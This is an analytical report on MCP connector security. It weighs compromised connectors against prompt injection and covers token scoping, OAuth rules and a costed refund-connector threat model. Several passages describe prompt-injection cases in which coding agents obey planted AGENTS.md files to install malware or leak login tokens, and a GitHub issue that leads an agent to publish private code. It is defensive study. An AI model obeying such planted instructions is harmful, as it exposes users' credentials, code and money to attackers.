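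OX discovered the problem in GPT Researcher, an open-source research tool that let users enter the launch command for their own connector. ITPro's *AI agents using Anthropic MCP could be a vector for supply chain* reports that OX's researchers entered an ordinary operating-system command instead. The tool returned an error because no connector had started, but the server had already run the command. Anyone who could fill in that setting could take over the server and any connector credentials stored on it.

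OX's researchers then ran commands on six live services belonging to real companies. They sent more than 30 reports to software developers and listed ten vulnerabilities, three of which had patches when OX published. Attackers could exploit some of the affected applications without logging in. In the code editor Windsurf, planted text could trigger a command on the user's computer without the user doing anything. OX estimated that up to 200,000 servers were vulnerable, but this figure doesn't measure how many were attacked.

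OX asked Anthropic to change the kits to run only approved commands. Anthropic declined, saying this wasn't a valid vulnerability because it "requires explicit user permission for the file change". It also described the launch mechanism as a secure default and said developers were responsible for checking what users enter. Anthropic and LangChain, whose framework GPT Researcher used, called the behaviour expected. Anthropic later updated its security policy to advise caution with stdio connectors.

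Anthropic's argument is reasonable for a person who edits the settings on their own laptop. The setting exists to start a program, and that person could run the same command without MCP. The argument is much weaker for a website where a stranger enters the command and the company's server runs it. The stranger may well give permission, but the machine belongs to the company. The Windsurf case is hard to reconcile with Anthropic's reply, since the user took no action.

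But OX's remedy would probably achieve less than OX claims. It argued that a list of approved commands in the official kits would instantly protect every project built on them. A practical list would have to include `npx`, because many connectors start with it, but `npx` can download and run almost any package. OX itself got past such a list in Upsonic, an agent framework, by adding extra inputs to `npx` or `npm`. A list would still block the crudest attacks, such as the one on GPT Researcher, but developers would have to restrict the inputs as well as the command. OX also gives developers stricter and more convincing advice, which is to keep user input out of the launch settings altogether or let users choose only from commands the developer has already set up.

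### Old connectors with known flaws

Some connectors have flaws that nobody intends to fix. Anthropic published a set of reference connectors in MCP's early days, and their maintainers archived several in May 2025. Glow Labs, a security research group, found four serious flaws in these archived connectors. The worst is in a connector that lets an agent control a web browser. A prompt injection can make the agent start any program in place of the browser, and the user's earlier approval of web browsing also covers this action. An attacker could use that program to take over the machine and everything the connector can reach.

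Agents help keep unmaintained connectors in use. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents are installing MCP servers that will never be patched* (2026) describes a session, documented by Glow Labs, in which a developer asked a coding agent to set up a GitHub connector. GitHub maintains one, but the agent installed the archived version, whose name it had apparently learned in training. In another session, an agent looked up a package, found a notice that it was deprecated, and installed it anyway without telling the user.

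Glow Labs attributes 98% of the installations it studied to names the model learned in training. It looked only at sessions in which an agent installed or suggested an outdated connector, so the figure doesn't show how often agents make this mistake. Users and automated systems have downloaded the outdated packages more than 17.3 million times since July 2025, which suggests that the mistake isn't rare. Glow Labs has so far seen no attacks that exploit the four flaws.

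npm's rules also prevent the owners from simply withdrawing the packages, because an owner can't remove one with 300 or more downloads in the past week. The archived GitHub connector had about 185,000.

### Expired domains

A remote connector's address usually includes a domain name, which the owner has to renew. If the registration lapses, anyone can buy the name and run a new server at the old address. Agents that still have the address in their settings will connect to the new server just as they did to the old one.

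In a survey it described in The Hacker News in October 2026, OX Security reduced 15,465 connectors from five registries to 5,095 separate hostnames, the part of a web address that identifies a server. About 2.3% of the hostnames, or roughly 117, no longer led to a server. Six of those were on expired domains that anyone could register for $4 to $12 a year.

Anyone who bought one of these domains would control a connector and could read whatever agents sent to it, without breaking into any account. If a user's host attached an API key for an outside service to each request, the buyer would receive the key too.

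There were only six domains, and OX didn't report that anyone had bought one for an attack. A registry entry also doesn't prove that anyone still uses the connector. But registering all six domains would cost an attacker at most $72 a year.

The survey also found that about 0.45% of the hostnames (about 23) used consumer services that make a personal computer reachable from the internet. OX thinks these connectors probably run on home networks. An attacker who broke into one of those computers would control the connector for everyone who used it.

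### Changed settings files

An attacker can add a malicious connector to an agent's settings instead of compromising an existing one. Coding agents read some settings from the project folder they open, so anyone who gives a developer a project can include settings in it. The security company Check Point found that a project file called `.mcp.json` could start a malicious connector in Claude Code without warning the developer. Another file could run an attacker's command as soon as the agent opened the project. Both flaws have been fixed, according to ETN's *Tekoälyagentti voidaan kaapata projektitiedostolla*, a Finnish report on the research. Check Point warns that many coding agents still trust settings files automatically, even those from a stranger's project.

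The agent can also make the change itself. Forever Security's *Markdown Is the New Executable* (October 2026) describes an attempted attack on one of the company's customers. Forever's software stopped a coding agent from installing function-color, a known malicious npm package. The agent was following instructions in an `AGENTS.md` file it had found in the customer's Downloads folder.

Developers write `AGENTS.md` files to tell coding agents how to work on a project, and OpenAI's coding agent Codex reads them when it starts. The attacker's file looked like ordinary engineering notes, and nobody knew how it had got onto the computer. Forever suspects that a website saved it, because a browser can save a file to the Downloads folder without a click, and operating systems don't treat a text file as a program that needs approval. Forever showed that this method works but didn't establish that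 the attacker had used it.

The company then opened Codex on an isolated virtual machine, in a folder containing the attacker's file. Codex rewrote its settings, then downloaded and ran the malicious package. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents fall for malicious instructions planted in the Downloads folder* (2026) adds that the new settings applied to the whole computer, so every later Codex session ran the attacker's command, in any project. A malicious local connector gives an attacker the same repeated access, because the host also runs it at every launch.

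Codex ran the malware, or a harmless substitute that opened a calculator, in more than 90% of Forever's attempts. Most attempts used the substitute. The file's length seems to have helped the attack, because Codex refused a short request to install the package.

Claude Code was harder to fool. Forever wrote a different file for it, which presented the new setting as the address of a company's internal gateway. Claude Code made the change in about half the tests and then sent its requests, including the user's login token, to a server Forever controlled. The researchers used a captured token to take over the account.

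Both attacks start as prompt injections, since a model that ignored the planted file would have prevented them. But once the settings have changed, a better model no longer helps.

Forever seems too pessimistic in arguing that OpenAI and Anthropic have nothing to patch, because an agent that obeys an `AGENTS.md` file is working as designed. An agent can follow a project's instructions about code without being free to rewrite its own settings. Claude Code normally asks a person to approve such a change, and a host could prevent the model from editing those settings at all. Until hosts do so, Forever advises keeping coding agents out of the Downloads folder, where about half of its customers run one.

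### Stolen tokens

An attacker who has a copy of a connector's token can use it without going through the connector. This happened in 2025 to companies that had linked Salesloft's Drift chat tool to their customer records. Some developers publish their tokens by accident. ETN reports that Check Point examined about 46,500 published software packages and found that 428 contained a Claude Code settings file the developer hadn't meant to include. About one in 13 of those files held working credentials for npm, GitHub or Hugging Face, a site that hosts AI models. An npm credential can be especially valuable because it may let an attacker publish a malicious update under the developer's name.

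Attackers have already used a leaked key to publish a malicious package. The Hacker News' *Leaked LiteLLM Master Key Let Attackers Steal GitHub Tokens and Hijack Release* (2026) describes an attack that began with a leaked master key, which gives administrator access to a LiteLLM server and which nobody had revoked. The attackers used the key to steal GitHub tokens, took over the system that published a software project's releases, and put a malicious version on PyPI. That version installed a back door on users' computers and stole their credentials. Attackers could have used any of those credentials for another attack of the same kind.

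## When is a compromised connector worse than an injected prompt?

An attacker who controls a connector can usually do more damage in one incident than an attacker who plants text in a ticket. But planting text takes almost no effort, and far more people can try it. A company choosing which threat to tackle first is weighing a rare, large loss against frequent, smaller ones.

The argument that a compromised connector is worse than an injected prompt has four premises: the attacker uses the connector's authority directly, better models don't stop the attack, the attack can affect every call, and the connector can return false reports. All four are broadly true, but each faces an objection that limits how far it applies.

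### Using authority directly

An attacker who controls the shop's refund connector has its payment key and can send refund requests to the processor without deceiving anyone. The Salesloft Drift token thefts, which Sophos' *AI Security 2026* (2026) cites, gave attackers the same kind of direct access.

But a deceived agent can often act with the same authority. Park's *Pwning Agentic AI Part I* describes a company that isolates its database, restricts outgoing traffic and keeps its credentials in a vault. An attacker files a support ticket containing instructions. The agent reads it during routine triage, then copies every login token in the production database into a public comment thread. No alert fires because the agent uses its own account and approved tools. In another of Park's attacks, a ticket makes the agent encrypt every customer's email address with a key that only the attacker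 has. Both are researchers' demonstrations, but the attacker only has to file a ticket.

A deceived agent may give an attacker wider reach than a compromised connector. CYFIRMA's *Exploitation of Model Context Protocol in Agentic AI Deployments* points out that an agent works with the combined permissions of all its connectors. An attacker who plants a ticket at the shop could get the agent to use the ticket reader, the mail sender and the refund connector together, while an attacker who controls only the refund connector and can't get out of its sandbox has just the payment key.

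An agent misled by an injected prompt can request only the operations that its connectors offer, and an uncompromised connector can still reject those requests. If a refund connector's code rejects any refund above $100, an injected prompt can't get a larger one through, but an attacker who controls the code can delete that check. A compromised connector is therefore worse when its credential permits more than its tools do. If a database connector already runs any query the agent writes, an attacker who can inject prompts gains little by also taking over the connector.

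### What better models change

A model can't refuse an action that happens inside the connector, as the blind copy showed, and it can also misjudge a connector it has come to trust. *TrustShiftProbe* (2026) tested six leading agents with connectors that were benign at first and then turned malicious, and found them substantially susceptible. A monitor between the agent and the connector reduced the attacks that relied on deception. When a connector stopped doing its job, the monitor could detect the failure but not prevent it.

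Better models haven't eliminated prompt injection either. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports on a public competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models. Every model failed, from 0.5% of attempts for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro, and more capable models weren't reliably more resistant. Gavish (2026) writes in *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* that indirect prompt injection isn't a problem a company solves and moves on from.

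So a company can't rely on the model to stop either threat. The choice of model still matters against injection, since the competition's best and worst results differ by a factor of 17.

### Acting on every call

The malicious postmark-mcp release copied every email its users sent, whereas a ticket containing an injected prompt usually affects one conversation. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, adds that a compromised server affects every agent that connects to it.

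Attackers can make up for a ticket's short life by sending more tickets. Dziemian and colleagues found attack strategies that worked in 21 of the competition's 41 scenarios and on several families of models. An attacker who finds wording that works can therefore reuse it, perhaps against many companies.

Constant activity also makes an attacker who controls a connector easier to detect. Blind-copying every message leaves thousands of entries in the mail service's records, where an administrator could find them. A careful attacker would act only on valuable messages, losing part of the advantage of being able to act on every one.

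### False reports

*From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (2026) gives an example from a building's access system. A user asks which doors Emma can open. The agent asks a malicious connector for Emma's passkey, and the connector returns John's instead. The agent then writes a database query with John's passkey. The query is written correctly, so anyone who checked it would find no mistake, but it returns John's doors, which the agent presents as Emma's.

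A deceived model can mislead its user too. In most of the competition's scenarios, an attack counted as a success only if the model's final reply also concealed it. In one scenario, a planted email contained instructions for an assistant to mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. The user would have seen an ordinary summary and missed the deadline.

So the two threats look much the same to someone who reads only the agent's replies. An investigator has an easier job after an injection because the host's log contains the harmful call, but Dziemian and colleagues warn that these logs are often too long and complex for people to inspect effectively.

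### Spread from a low-risk connector

A connector with little authority should be able to do little harm. If an attacker took over a remote connector that only looks up exchange rates, the shop might get some wrong prices, but it would not lose its payment key, because the connector never had it.

The Australian Signals Directorate and its partner agencies describe a hypothetical case in which a minor tool leads to a serious loss. An organisation uses an agent to approve purchases and write to suppliers. To avoid delays, it gives the agent broad access to financial systems, email and contracts, and reviews those permissions only once, at deployment. Other agents gradually come to rely on the purchasing agent's output.

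An attacker compromises a low-risk tool in the agent's workflow and inherits the agent's privileges. The attacker changes contracts and approves payments without triggering an alert. The audit logs look legitimate because every action appears under the agent's identity.

Which threat the scenario illustrates depends on how the tool inherits those privileges, and the agencies don't say exactly how it does. If the tool and the agent share a credential, the attacker can approve payments directly. If the tool has only a weak credential of its own, the attacker has to trick the agent into making the payment. The agencies mention "carefully crafted requests" and call the attack a confused deputy, which suggests the second reading. In that case, a model that ignored the requests would prevent the loss.

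Their other scenario depends less on the model. A company adds a third-party scheduling component to a customer support agent and grants it broad access at start-up. The system then relies on that approval instead of checking each request. An attacker compromises the component and gets into neighbouring agents that handle billing and refunds, because the company hasn't separated them properly.

An attack can also spread through the model, as in the WhatsApp case. *MCP-ITP* (2026) explains that this is possible because the host loads legitimate and malicious tool descriptions into the same prompt.

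A widely repeated statistic about this kind of spread is that attacks succeed 78.3% of the time when an agent has five connectors. Cycode's *OWASP MCP Top 10* (2026) credits it to Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, and Dhamsania (2026), in *MCP has tightened its authentication rules four times*, repeats the credit. The figure actually comes from Maloyan and Namiot, who gave an attacker control of one connector and varied the total number:

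| Connectors attached | Attacks that succeeded | Attacks that spread to another connector's operations |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 47.8% | Not applicable |
| 2 | 58.4% | 34.2% |
| 3 | 67.1% | 51.8% |
| 5 | 78.3% | 72.4% |

These attacks fed malicious text to the model, so the results don't cover an attacker who uses a connector's key directly. The models tested were Claude 3.5 Sonnet, GPT-4o and Llama 3.1 70B, all from 2024, and current models would probably resist more often. The upward trend is more informative than the 78.3% figure, because each added connector is something else that an injected prompt can make the model misuse.

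Maloyan and Namiot also measured the effect of having the host restrict data flow between connectors. With no restriction, 61.3% of attacks that crossed from one connector to another succeeded. Asking the user to approve each transfer cut that to 31.7%, and blocking all transfers cut it to 8.7%. But the restrictions also reduced the share of tasks that agents completed, from 94.2% to 87.4% with approvals and 61.8% with the full block. A shop that wants its agent to read a ticket and then issue a refund can't block every transfer.

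### How often each attack happens

Most of the evidence on injection is about attempts. Check Point Research's *AI Security Report 2026* (2026) shows that detections of longer malicious prompts rose about fivefold between March and May 2026, to nearly 1% of the prompts the company observed. Check Point treats length as a sign of indirect injection because attacks hidden in documents or aimed at agents tend to be longer. That inference is reasonable, but the company counted detections, not successful attacks.

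Google looked for injections in an archive of public web pages and found 32% more malicious ones in February 2026 than in November 2025. Most were crude. Some were instructions for the reader's AI assistant to delete all the files on the machine, and Google thought these were unlikely to work. The archive leaves out most social media and wouldn't contain private inboxes or support queues, where an attacker would target the shop.

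For connectors, most of the figures describe weaknesses:

- Check Point Research's *Cyber Security Report 2026* (2026) found that 40% of the MCP servers it analysed were vulnerable.
- TrendAI Research's *Hunt Them All* estimated that 3.1% to 8.6% of more than 19,000 MCP code repositories had flaws an attacker could exploit.
- *Exposed by Design* (2026) audited 414 live servers in July 2026 and reported signs of tool poisoning in 47 of them.

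The gap between the first two figures probably reflects how strictly each team defined a vulnerability. TrendAI Research used AI to search for flaws and concluded that only 4.1% of those flagged were exploitable. None of the three figures measures the chance that an attacker will take over a particular connector within a year. Lists of known malicious connectors don't provide it either, because nobody knows how many agents ran them.

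IBM (2026) studied 602 organisations that had suffered data breaches, and more than 20% reported one that targeted AI models or applications. Compromised APIs, applications or plug-ins caused 27% of those AI breaches, tying with badly configured cloud services as the leading cause. ASIS International's *Global Data Breach Costs Drop* reports that a similar category was the most common cause in the previous year's survey, at 30%. The category covers much more than agent connectors, and the 27% represents only a few dozen organisations.

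IBM's cost figures suggest that a prompt injection sometimes costs at least as much as a compromised connector. IBM's *AI‑powered adversaries and the enterprise risk challenge* (2026) puts the average cost of a prompt injection incident at $5.89 million, the second highest of any type of attack on AI. The average for all incidents involving AI was $5.33 million, according to Joos (2026). These averages include only injections that ended in a breach, not the many that failed.

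OWASP, a non-profit that publishes lists of common software risks, lists ten for MCP. Gorgiev and Sutton (2026), in *Mapping NSA's MCP guidance to the OWASP MCP Top 10*, a blog post from the security testing company Equixly, place only two of them, tool poisoning and prompt injection, in the text an agent reads. They place the other eight in areas such as credentials, dependencies and logging. Dhamsania attributes this count to the NSA, but the NSA guidance doesn't contain it. The count shows that filtering text leaves many risks uncovered, but it doesn't measure how often any of the ten leads to an attack or how much damage follows.

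### Expected loss at the shop

A rough formula makes the two threats comparable:

expected yearly loss = chance of compromise × authority reached × exposure

Authority reached is the most money the attacker could make the shop lose. Exposure is the fraction of that loss the attacker causes before the shop cuts off access. For repeated attacks, such as attacks through tickets, the expected number of successes per year replaces the chance of compromise.

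Suppose the shop receives 1,000 malicious tickets a year and 0.5% of them succeed, the lowest rate in the competition. Each successful ticket causes the agent to issue $2,000 in false refunds, the value of about 50 average orders. Suppose also that the refund connector has a 1% chance of being compromised each year, and that anyone holding its key can refund all $600,000 in past charges. Refunds normally go back to the card that paid, so the attacker might need accomplices to profit, but the shop loses the money either way.

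| | Malicious tickets | Compromised refund connector |
|---|---|---|
| Expected successes per year | 5 | 0.01 |
| Authority reached each time | $2,000 | $600,000 |
| Exposure | 1 | 1 |
| Expected yearly loss | $10,000 | $6,000 |
| Largest single loss | $2,000 | $600,000 |

On average, the tickets cost more, but the connector's worst event is 300 times as large. In 99 years out of 100, the shop would lose nothing to the connector and might conclude that it was safe.

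The ranking by averages is fragile, because every input is uncertain:

| Change to one assumption | Tickets | Connector |
|---|---|---|
| 0.1% of tickets succeed | $2,000 | $6,000 |
| 8.5% of tickets succeed | $170,000 | $6,000 |
| The connector has a 2% yearly chance of compromise | $10,000 | $12,000 |
| The shop cancels the key after a tenth of the money has gone | $10,000 | $600 |

The 0.1% is Anthropic's figure for a single attempt against Opus 4.7. The 8.5% is the worst result in the competition and is probably too high for an ordinary support desk. Contestants could see the conversation and knew exactly which action they had to trigger, so Dziemian and colleagues describe their results as an upper bound. The 1% for the connector is an assumption. If the true chance is above about 1.7%, or one in 60, the connector is worse on average as well.

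The $2,000 limit on each ticket also holds only if something enforces it. Without a cap on the agent's refunds, one successful ticket could request far more, or an attacker could send the same wording 300 times, and the worst case for tickets would approach $600,000 too. A cap in the refund connector's code would prevent this unless an attacker had taken over the connector.

Comparing average losses makes sense for someone who can spread the risk. An insurer covering 1,000 such shops would expect to pay about $10 million a year for tickets and $6 million for connectors, and could reasonably worry more about the tickets. That changes if all the shops use the same refund connector and install its updates automatically. One malicious release could then hit every shop in the same week and cost the insurer $600 million. Connector losses would still average $6 million a year, but the insurer would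 pay nothing for them in most years and might go bankrupt in the year of a malicious release.

A single shop can't spread the risk. If it couldn't survive a $600,000 loss, it should limit the refund connector first, even though the tickets are likely to cost it more in an ordinary year.

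## What should a connector be allowed to do?

The shop's refund connector pays out about $4,000 a day, but its key allows $600,000 in refunds. A thin connector, which offers a few narrow operations and has only the permissions they need, closes most of that gap.

Narrow operations limit an attacker who injects a prompt, and a narrow key limits one who controls the connector.

### Narrow operations

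A database connector might offer a tool called `run_query`, which runs any command the model writes. A deceived model could use it to read every customer's address or delete the order history. A tool that refunds one order by up to $100 has a much smaller worst case. Its schema could look like this:

```json
{ "name": "refund_order",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "order_id": { "type": "string", "pattern": "^[0-9]{4}$" },
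      "amount": { "type": "number", "exclusiveMinimum": 0, "maximum": 100 } },
    "required": ["order_id", "amount"],
    "additionalProperties": false } }
```

These typed parameters require a four-digit order number and an amount above zero and no more than 100. The last line rules out extra fields, such as a different card to receive the refund. Software can reject any call that breaks these rules, regardless of why the model made it. The July revision of Model Context Protocol (2026) added conditional rules to the schema language, so a shop could also require a reason code for any refund above $50.

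Giving an input a type helps only if the type allows less than the connector's own authority does. The input to `run_query` is typed as text, which can contain any command. The NSA recommends checking inputs against the situation as well as the schema. It gives the example of a mathematics tool whose sums look valid while an attacker alters a separate "context" parameter to make the tool read or write files. The schema above would accept a $100 refund on a $40 kettle, so the connector also has to look up the order and reject any refund larger than the customer paid.

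A tool that runs shell commands, the text commands that control a computer, is the extreme case of free-form access. In a March post on tool labels, Model Context Protocol (2026) warns that a single injected instruction could make an agent with an unrestricted shell leak data. It cites a demonstration that combined a malicious calendar event, a calendar connector and a tool that runs code. A support agent doesn't need a shell, but coding agents often do. Because the shell tool can't limit what they run, a sandbox has to.

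The shop can also use separate connectors for reading and writing. This limits a compromised connector only if each has its own credential, because connectors that share a key have the same authority. The NSA found that even MCP implementations that check a caller's identity often don't distinguish permission to read from permission to create, update or delete.

A read-only credential limits a connector more reliably than a "read-only" label. MCP lets a connector label its own tools as read-only, and some hosts skip the approval prompt for those tools. But a malicious connector can put the label on a tool that makes changes. GitHub's connector also has a read-only mode, which about 17% of users turn on. The mode helps against an injected prompt, but a malicious version of the connector could ignore it. If the token itself is read-only, GitHub will reject any change the connector tries to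 make.

A malicious connector can do a lot of harm even with read-only access. For example, it can copy every message in a mailbox to its operator.

### The GitHub connector's blanket access

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) shows what can happen when a connector has too much authority. A developer has public and private repositories (project folders on GitHub) and links an agent to them through GitHub's official connector. An attacker then files an issue (a bug report) in one of the public repositories.

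Willison quotes the issue in *GitHub MCP Exploited*. It contains a complaint that the project's author isn't widely recognised and an instruction to fix this by reading the README files in all the author's repositories and writing about them. When the developer asks the agent to look at open issues, the agent reads the private repositories and publishes details from them in the public repository.

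The connector had no bug. As heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains, it acted through the user's own account, so the agent could reach whatever the user could. Willison points out that this one connector supplied private data, exposure to an attacker's instructions and a way to send the data out. According to DevClass's *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP*, Invariant's researchers thought users could prevent the leak by carefully approving each action, but suspected that many choose "always allow".

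The NSA cites this case as one in which malicious or compromised tools could copy private code into public view, but Invariant Labs' attack used an injected prompt and a connector that was neither malicious nor compromised. The NSA's warning is still correct, because an attacker who controlled the connector would have had the same access without filing an issue or injecting a prompt.

A narrower token would have prevented the leak in either case. A commenter in the forum thread *GitHub MCP exploited* notes that GitHub offers tokens that cover a single repository. With a token for only the public repository, neither the agent nor the connector could have read the private ones.

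A developer who works on both kinds of repository could run two copies of the connector, each with its own token. This would limit an attacker who controlled one copy, provided a sandbox kept that copy from reading the other's token. The developer would also need to use the two copies in separate conversations, because otherwise the injected prompt could still make the model read private code through one and publish it through the other.

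### Limiting what a token permits

MCP's rules mostly cover the token that a host presents to a remote connector. If the connector is malicious, its own credential for the outside service matters more than that token, because the credential determines how much money or data the attacker can reach.

MCP's rules build on OAuth, the standard that lets a program use someone's account without knowing the password. A separate program called an authorization server checks who the user is, asks for consent and issues a token.

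Narrow scopes limit what a thief can do with a stolen token. A thief who finds a read-only token in a log file can't use it to issue refunds. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) describes step-up authorization, in which a host can start with few scopes and add more. When a call needs a permission the token lacks, the connector refuses the call and lists the required scopes. The host then requests a new token, usually with the user's consent, and tries again.

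This process has weak points. The connector writes the list of scopes, so a malicious one can request more access than it needs, and the user may approve it. If a connector lists no scopes when it first refuses a request, the host falls back on requesting every scope the connector publishes. The host also keeps earlier scopes when it adds new ones, so a token that could only read files at first may later be able to delete them.

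Scopes also describe kinds of operation, so a refund scope normally covers both a $40 refund and a $4,000 one. *MCP Auth vs Tool-Call Authorization After the 2026-07-28 Spec*, a blog post from Permit.io, argues that a separate policy has to decide whether each action should run. Permit.io sells authorization software for this, but the argument is sound because a malicious connector can use everything its own token permits, as often as the service allows.

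A token can also specify its audience, the one service that should accept it. Suppose the shop's login system issues the tokens for all three connectors and an attacker controls the ticket reader. The host sends the ticket reader a token with every call. If the refund connector accepted the same token, the attacker could use it to pose as the agent and order refunds.

*OAuth Resource Indicators* (Campbell, 2020; RFC 8707) lets the host prevent this. When the host requests a token, it specifies which connector the token is for, and the authorization server records that in the token. The refund connector then rejects the token because it was issued for the ticket reader.

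MCP requires hosts to state which service a token is for, and connectors to check that the tokens they receive were issued for them. But as Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) acknowledges, this protection depends on the authorization server supporting it, and the host can't easily tell whether it does. *OAuth 2.0 Resource Parameter in Access Token Response* (McGuinness and Hanson, 2026) proposes that the server's reply should confirm which service the token is for. Even when this check works, it protects only the other connectors. A malicious refund connector can still use its payment key at the payment processor, where the key is valid.

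### Limiting who can use a token, and for how long

Short lifetimes protect against old copies, because a token that expires after an hour is useless to a thief who finds it in last week's backup. MCP only recommends short lifetimes, but it requires authorization servers to replace a refresh token each time an app that can't keep a secret, such as a desktop program, uses it.

An hour may be long enough for a prepared attacker. At ten requests a second, an attacker could refund the shop's $600,000 in past charges, as 15,000 refunds of $40, in 25 minutes. A malicious connector also gets a new token whenever the old one expires, for as long as it keeps running. Dhamsania recommends that connectors fetch credentials for each call instead of loading them at start-up. This leaves less for a thief to find in an uncompromised connector's memory, but a malicious connector can fetch credentials too.

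Some connectors take the user's token from the host and pass it unchanged to the outside service. The Model Context Protocol forbids this, which it calls token passthrough. The token has to work at both the connector and the service, so anyone who steals it from one can use it at the other. The service's logs may also attribute the connector's requests to the wrong program, and a caller with the token can bypass the connector's rate limits by calling the service directly.

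Token exchange is a safer alternative. The connector sends the user's token to an authorization server, which checks it and issues a different token for one outside service, with only the scopes the task needs. According to API Evangelist (2026), the standard for this, RFC 8693, is part of MCP's current roadmap. For now, MCP requires the connector to use a separate token at the outside service but doesn't specify how the connector gets it.

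If a mail connector that used token exchange turned malicious, it could act only for people whose tokens it had recently received, and only at services the authorization server allowed. A malicious connector with a fixed key to the company's mail system could open every mailbox at any time. Token exchange wouldn't protect people using the connector during the attack.

Key binding makes a copied token useless by itself. Bearer tokens lack this protection, and the draft standard *EPOP* (2026) calls their theft a practical attack. *OAuth 2.0 Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP)* (Fett, Campbell and colleagues, 2023) describes a way to tie a token to a cryptographic key. The program using the token creates a key pair and keeps the private key, and the authorization server links the token to the public key. For every request, the program signs a short message with the private key, and the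 service checks the signature, which a thief who copied the token from a log can't produce.

A malicious connector can use a token bound to a private key because it can also use the key. Binding still helps if the key is stored in hardware that never releases it. The attacker then can't use the token elsewhere and has to send every request through the running connector, so stopping the connector also ends the attacker's access. A copied bearer token would keep working until it expired or the issuer revoked it.

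The Model Context Protocol (MCP) hasn't adopted key binding yet. Its July 2026 rules still describe bearer tokens, and its August roadmap lists DPoP as work to finish. According to the roadmap, MCP authorization is designed for a person to approve access in a browser. Many agents now run with nobody present, and the maintainers want to give them their own identities instead of pasted API keys and long-lived tokens.

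### MCP's authorization rules since 2024

When MCP launched in November 2024, it had no authorization framework, and developers handled authorization themselves. The following March, Model Context Protocol (2025) added an optional framework based on OAuth, in which a connector could issue the tokens that it later accepted. The framework recommended that tokens expire but didn't require it, and had no rule tying a token to one connector.

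In June, Model Context Protocol (2025) required hosts to implement RFC 8707 to keep malicious connectors from obtaining tokens. The same revision stopped connectors from issuing tokens themselves. According to Parecki (2025), an OAuth specialist, a dedicated authorization server now handles both logins and tokens. Connectors therefore no longer decide what their tokens permit. In November, Model Context Protocol (2025) added the step-up process for scopes.

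The July 2026 revision dealt mainly with confusion between authorization servers. A host may use dozens of connectors, each with a different authorization server. An attacker who runs one of those servers may be able to trick the host into sending it a login code issued by an honest server. Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) lists two defences. The host must check the issuer's name on each reply, and it must not reuse one issuer's client credentials with another. The name check works only if the honest server includes its name in the reply. The revision recommends this, and a later one will probably require it.

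*Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* (Tabata, 2026) concludes that the revision introduced no fundamentally new ideas and mostly clarified how to apply existing OAuth practice. That seems right, and companies have used these methods for years, which is a good reason to trust the rules.

But the rules don't cover the most exposed connectors. The specification still makes authorization optional, and it tells developers of ordinary local connectors to take credentials from the environment instead of following these rules. The postmark-mcp package ran on its users' own machines and held a key to their mail service, and none of the rules would have limited what that key could do.

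The July revision may even leave some connectors with more secrets, because it began phasing out sampling, a feature that let a connector use the host's access to a language model. Descope's *What the July 2026 MCP Revision Means for Identity* points out that such connectors will now need their own keys from an AI company, which someone has to store, replace and cancel.

### Redesigning the refund connector

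The shop can now replace its refund connector with a thin one. The new connector's only tool is the `refund_order` tool above, with a limit of $100 per refund and 150 refunds in any 24 hours. It can return money only to the card used for the purchase. Its new key permits refunds and order look-ups, but not new charges or transfers to a bank account.

| | Original connector | Thin connector |
|---|---|---|
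| Largest single refund | Any past charge in full | $100 |
| Refunds in any 24 hours | No limit | 150 |
| Worst loss in 24 hours | $600,000 | $15,000 |
| Shortest time to lose $600,000 | 25 minutes at ten requests a second | 40 days |

These figures hold only if something other than the connector enforces the caps.

The 24 hours have to be a moving window. If the count reset at midnight, an attacker could send 150 refunds just before midnight and 150 just after and take $30,000 in a few minutes.

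The shop also has to guard against accidental repeats. Under the July 2026 revision, if a host's connection breaks during a call, the host has to send the call again under a new number to get the result. The connector might then treat the two calls as separate requests and refund the same kettle twice. The NSA warns that MCP leaves this problem to developers. Capping total refunds at what the customer paid would prevent a second full refund, but two partial refunds could both go through, so the connector should also detect repeated requests.

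At the 1% yearly chance of compromise assumed earlier, the expected loss falls from $6,000 a year to $150 if the shop notices within a day, or $1,050 if it takes a week. The largest single loss matters more to a small business than the expected loss, and the shop could probably survive the $15,000 it would lose in a day.

The caps are less effective against malicious tickets. Five successful tickets a year, each producing 50 false refunds of $40, would still cost $10,000, because 50 extra refunds fit within the daily limit. A limit of one refund per ticket would cut that to at most $500, as long as the host supplies the ticket number. If the model supplied it, an injected prompt could get the model to use other customers' ticket numbers.

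A patient attacker could also stay under the caps. The agent makes 100 refunds on a normal day, which leaves 50 for the attacker. At $100 each, the attacker could steal $5,000 a day, or $150,000 in a month, without causing any honest customer to be refused a refund. The caps give the shop time to notice a theft, but someone still has to review the refunds.

### What thin connectors cost

The most visible drawback of the caps is that they block some legitimate work. If a customer returns a $180 coffee machine, a staff member has to make the refund with a separate login. If a faulty batch of kettles brings 300 returns in one day, the agent stops halfway. The shop could raise the limit to 300, but that would double the worst daily loss to $30,000. An attacker could also use up the allowance to block honest refunds for a day, though this would do far less damage than the original connector allowed.

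Splitting connectors creates more programs to update and more credentials to manage. Each new package is also another one an attacker might compromise, though the attacker would gain less from it. Cutting the number of tools has a benefit apart from security. Model Context Protocol's roadmap notes that models tend to choose tools less well as the list grows, and a long list costs more to process. Splitting the same tools among more connectors doesn't shorten the list.

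Narrow permissions can also mean more consent screens, and users who see too many may approve them all without reading. The Model Context Protocol's security guidance recommends that connectors ask for related scopes together to reduce the number of requests. This is a reasonable compromise, but it gives each token some permissions that the current task doesn't need.

Large organisations also have a problem that Descope calls consent sprawl. Each employee approves each connector separately, and administrators can't see or withdraw the approvals in one place. An MCP extension called Enterprise-Managed Authorization moves the decision to the company's login system. The employee signs in once, and the host requests access to a connector from the login system. The login system applies the administrator's policy and issues a signed statement, which the connector's authorization server checks before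 issuing its own token with limited scopes. Anthropic supports this in its products. Employees see fewer prompts, but if an administrator grants too much access, everyone covered by the policy gets it.

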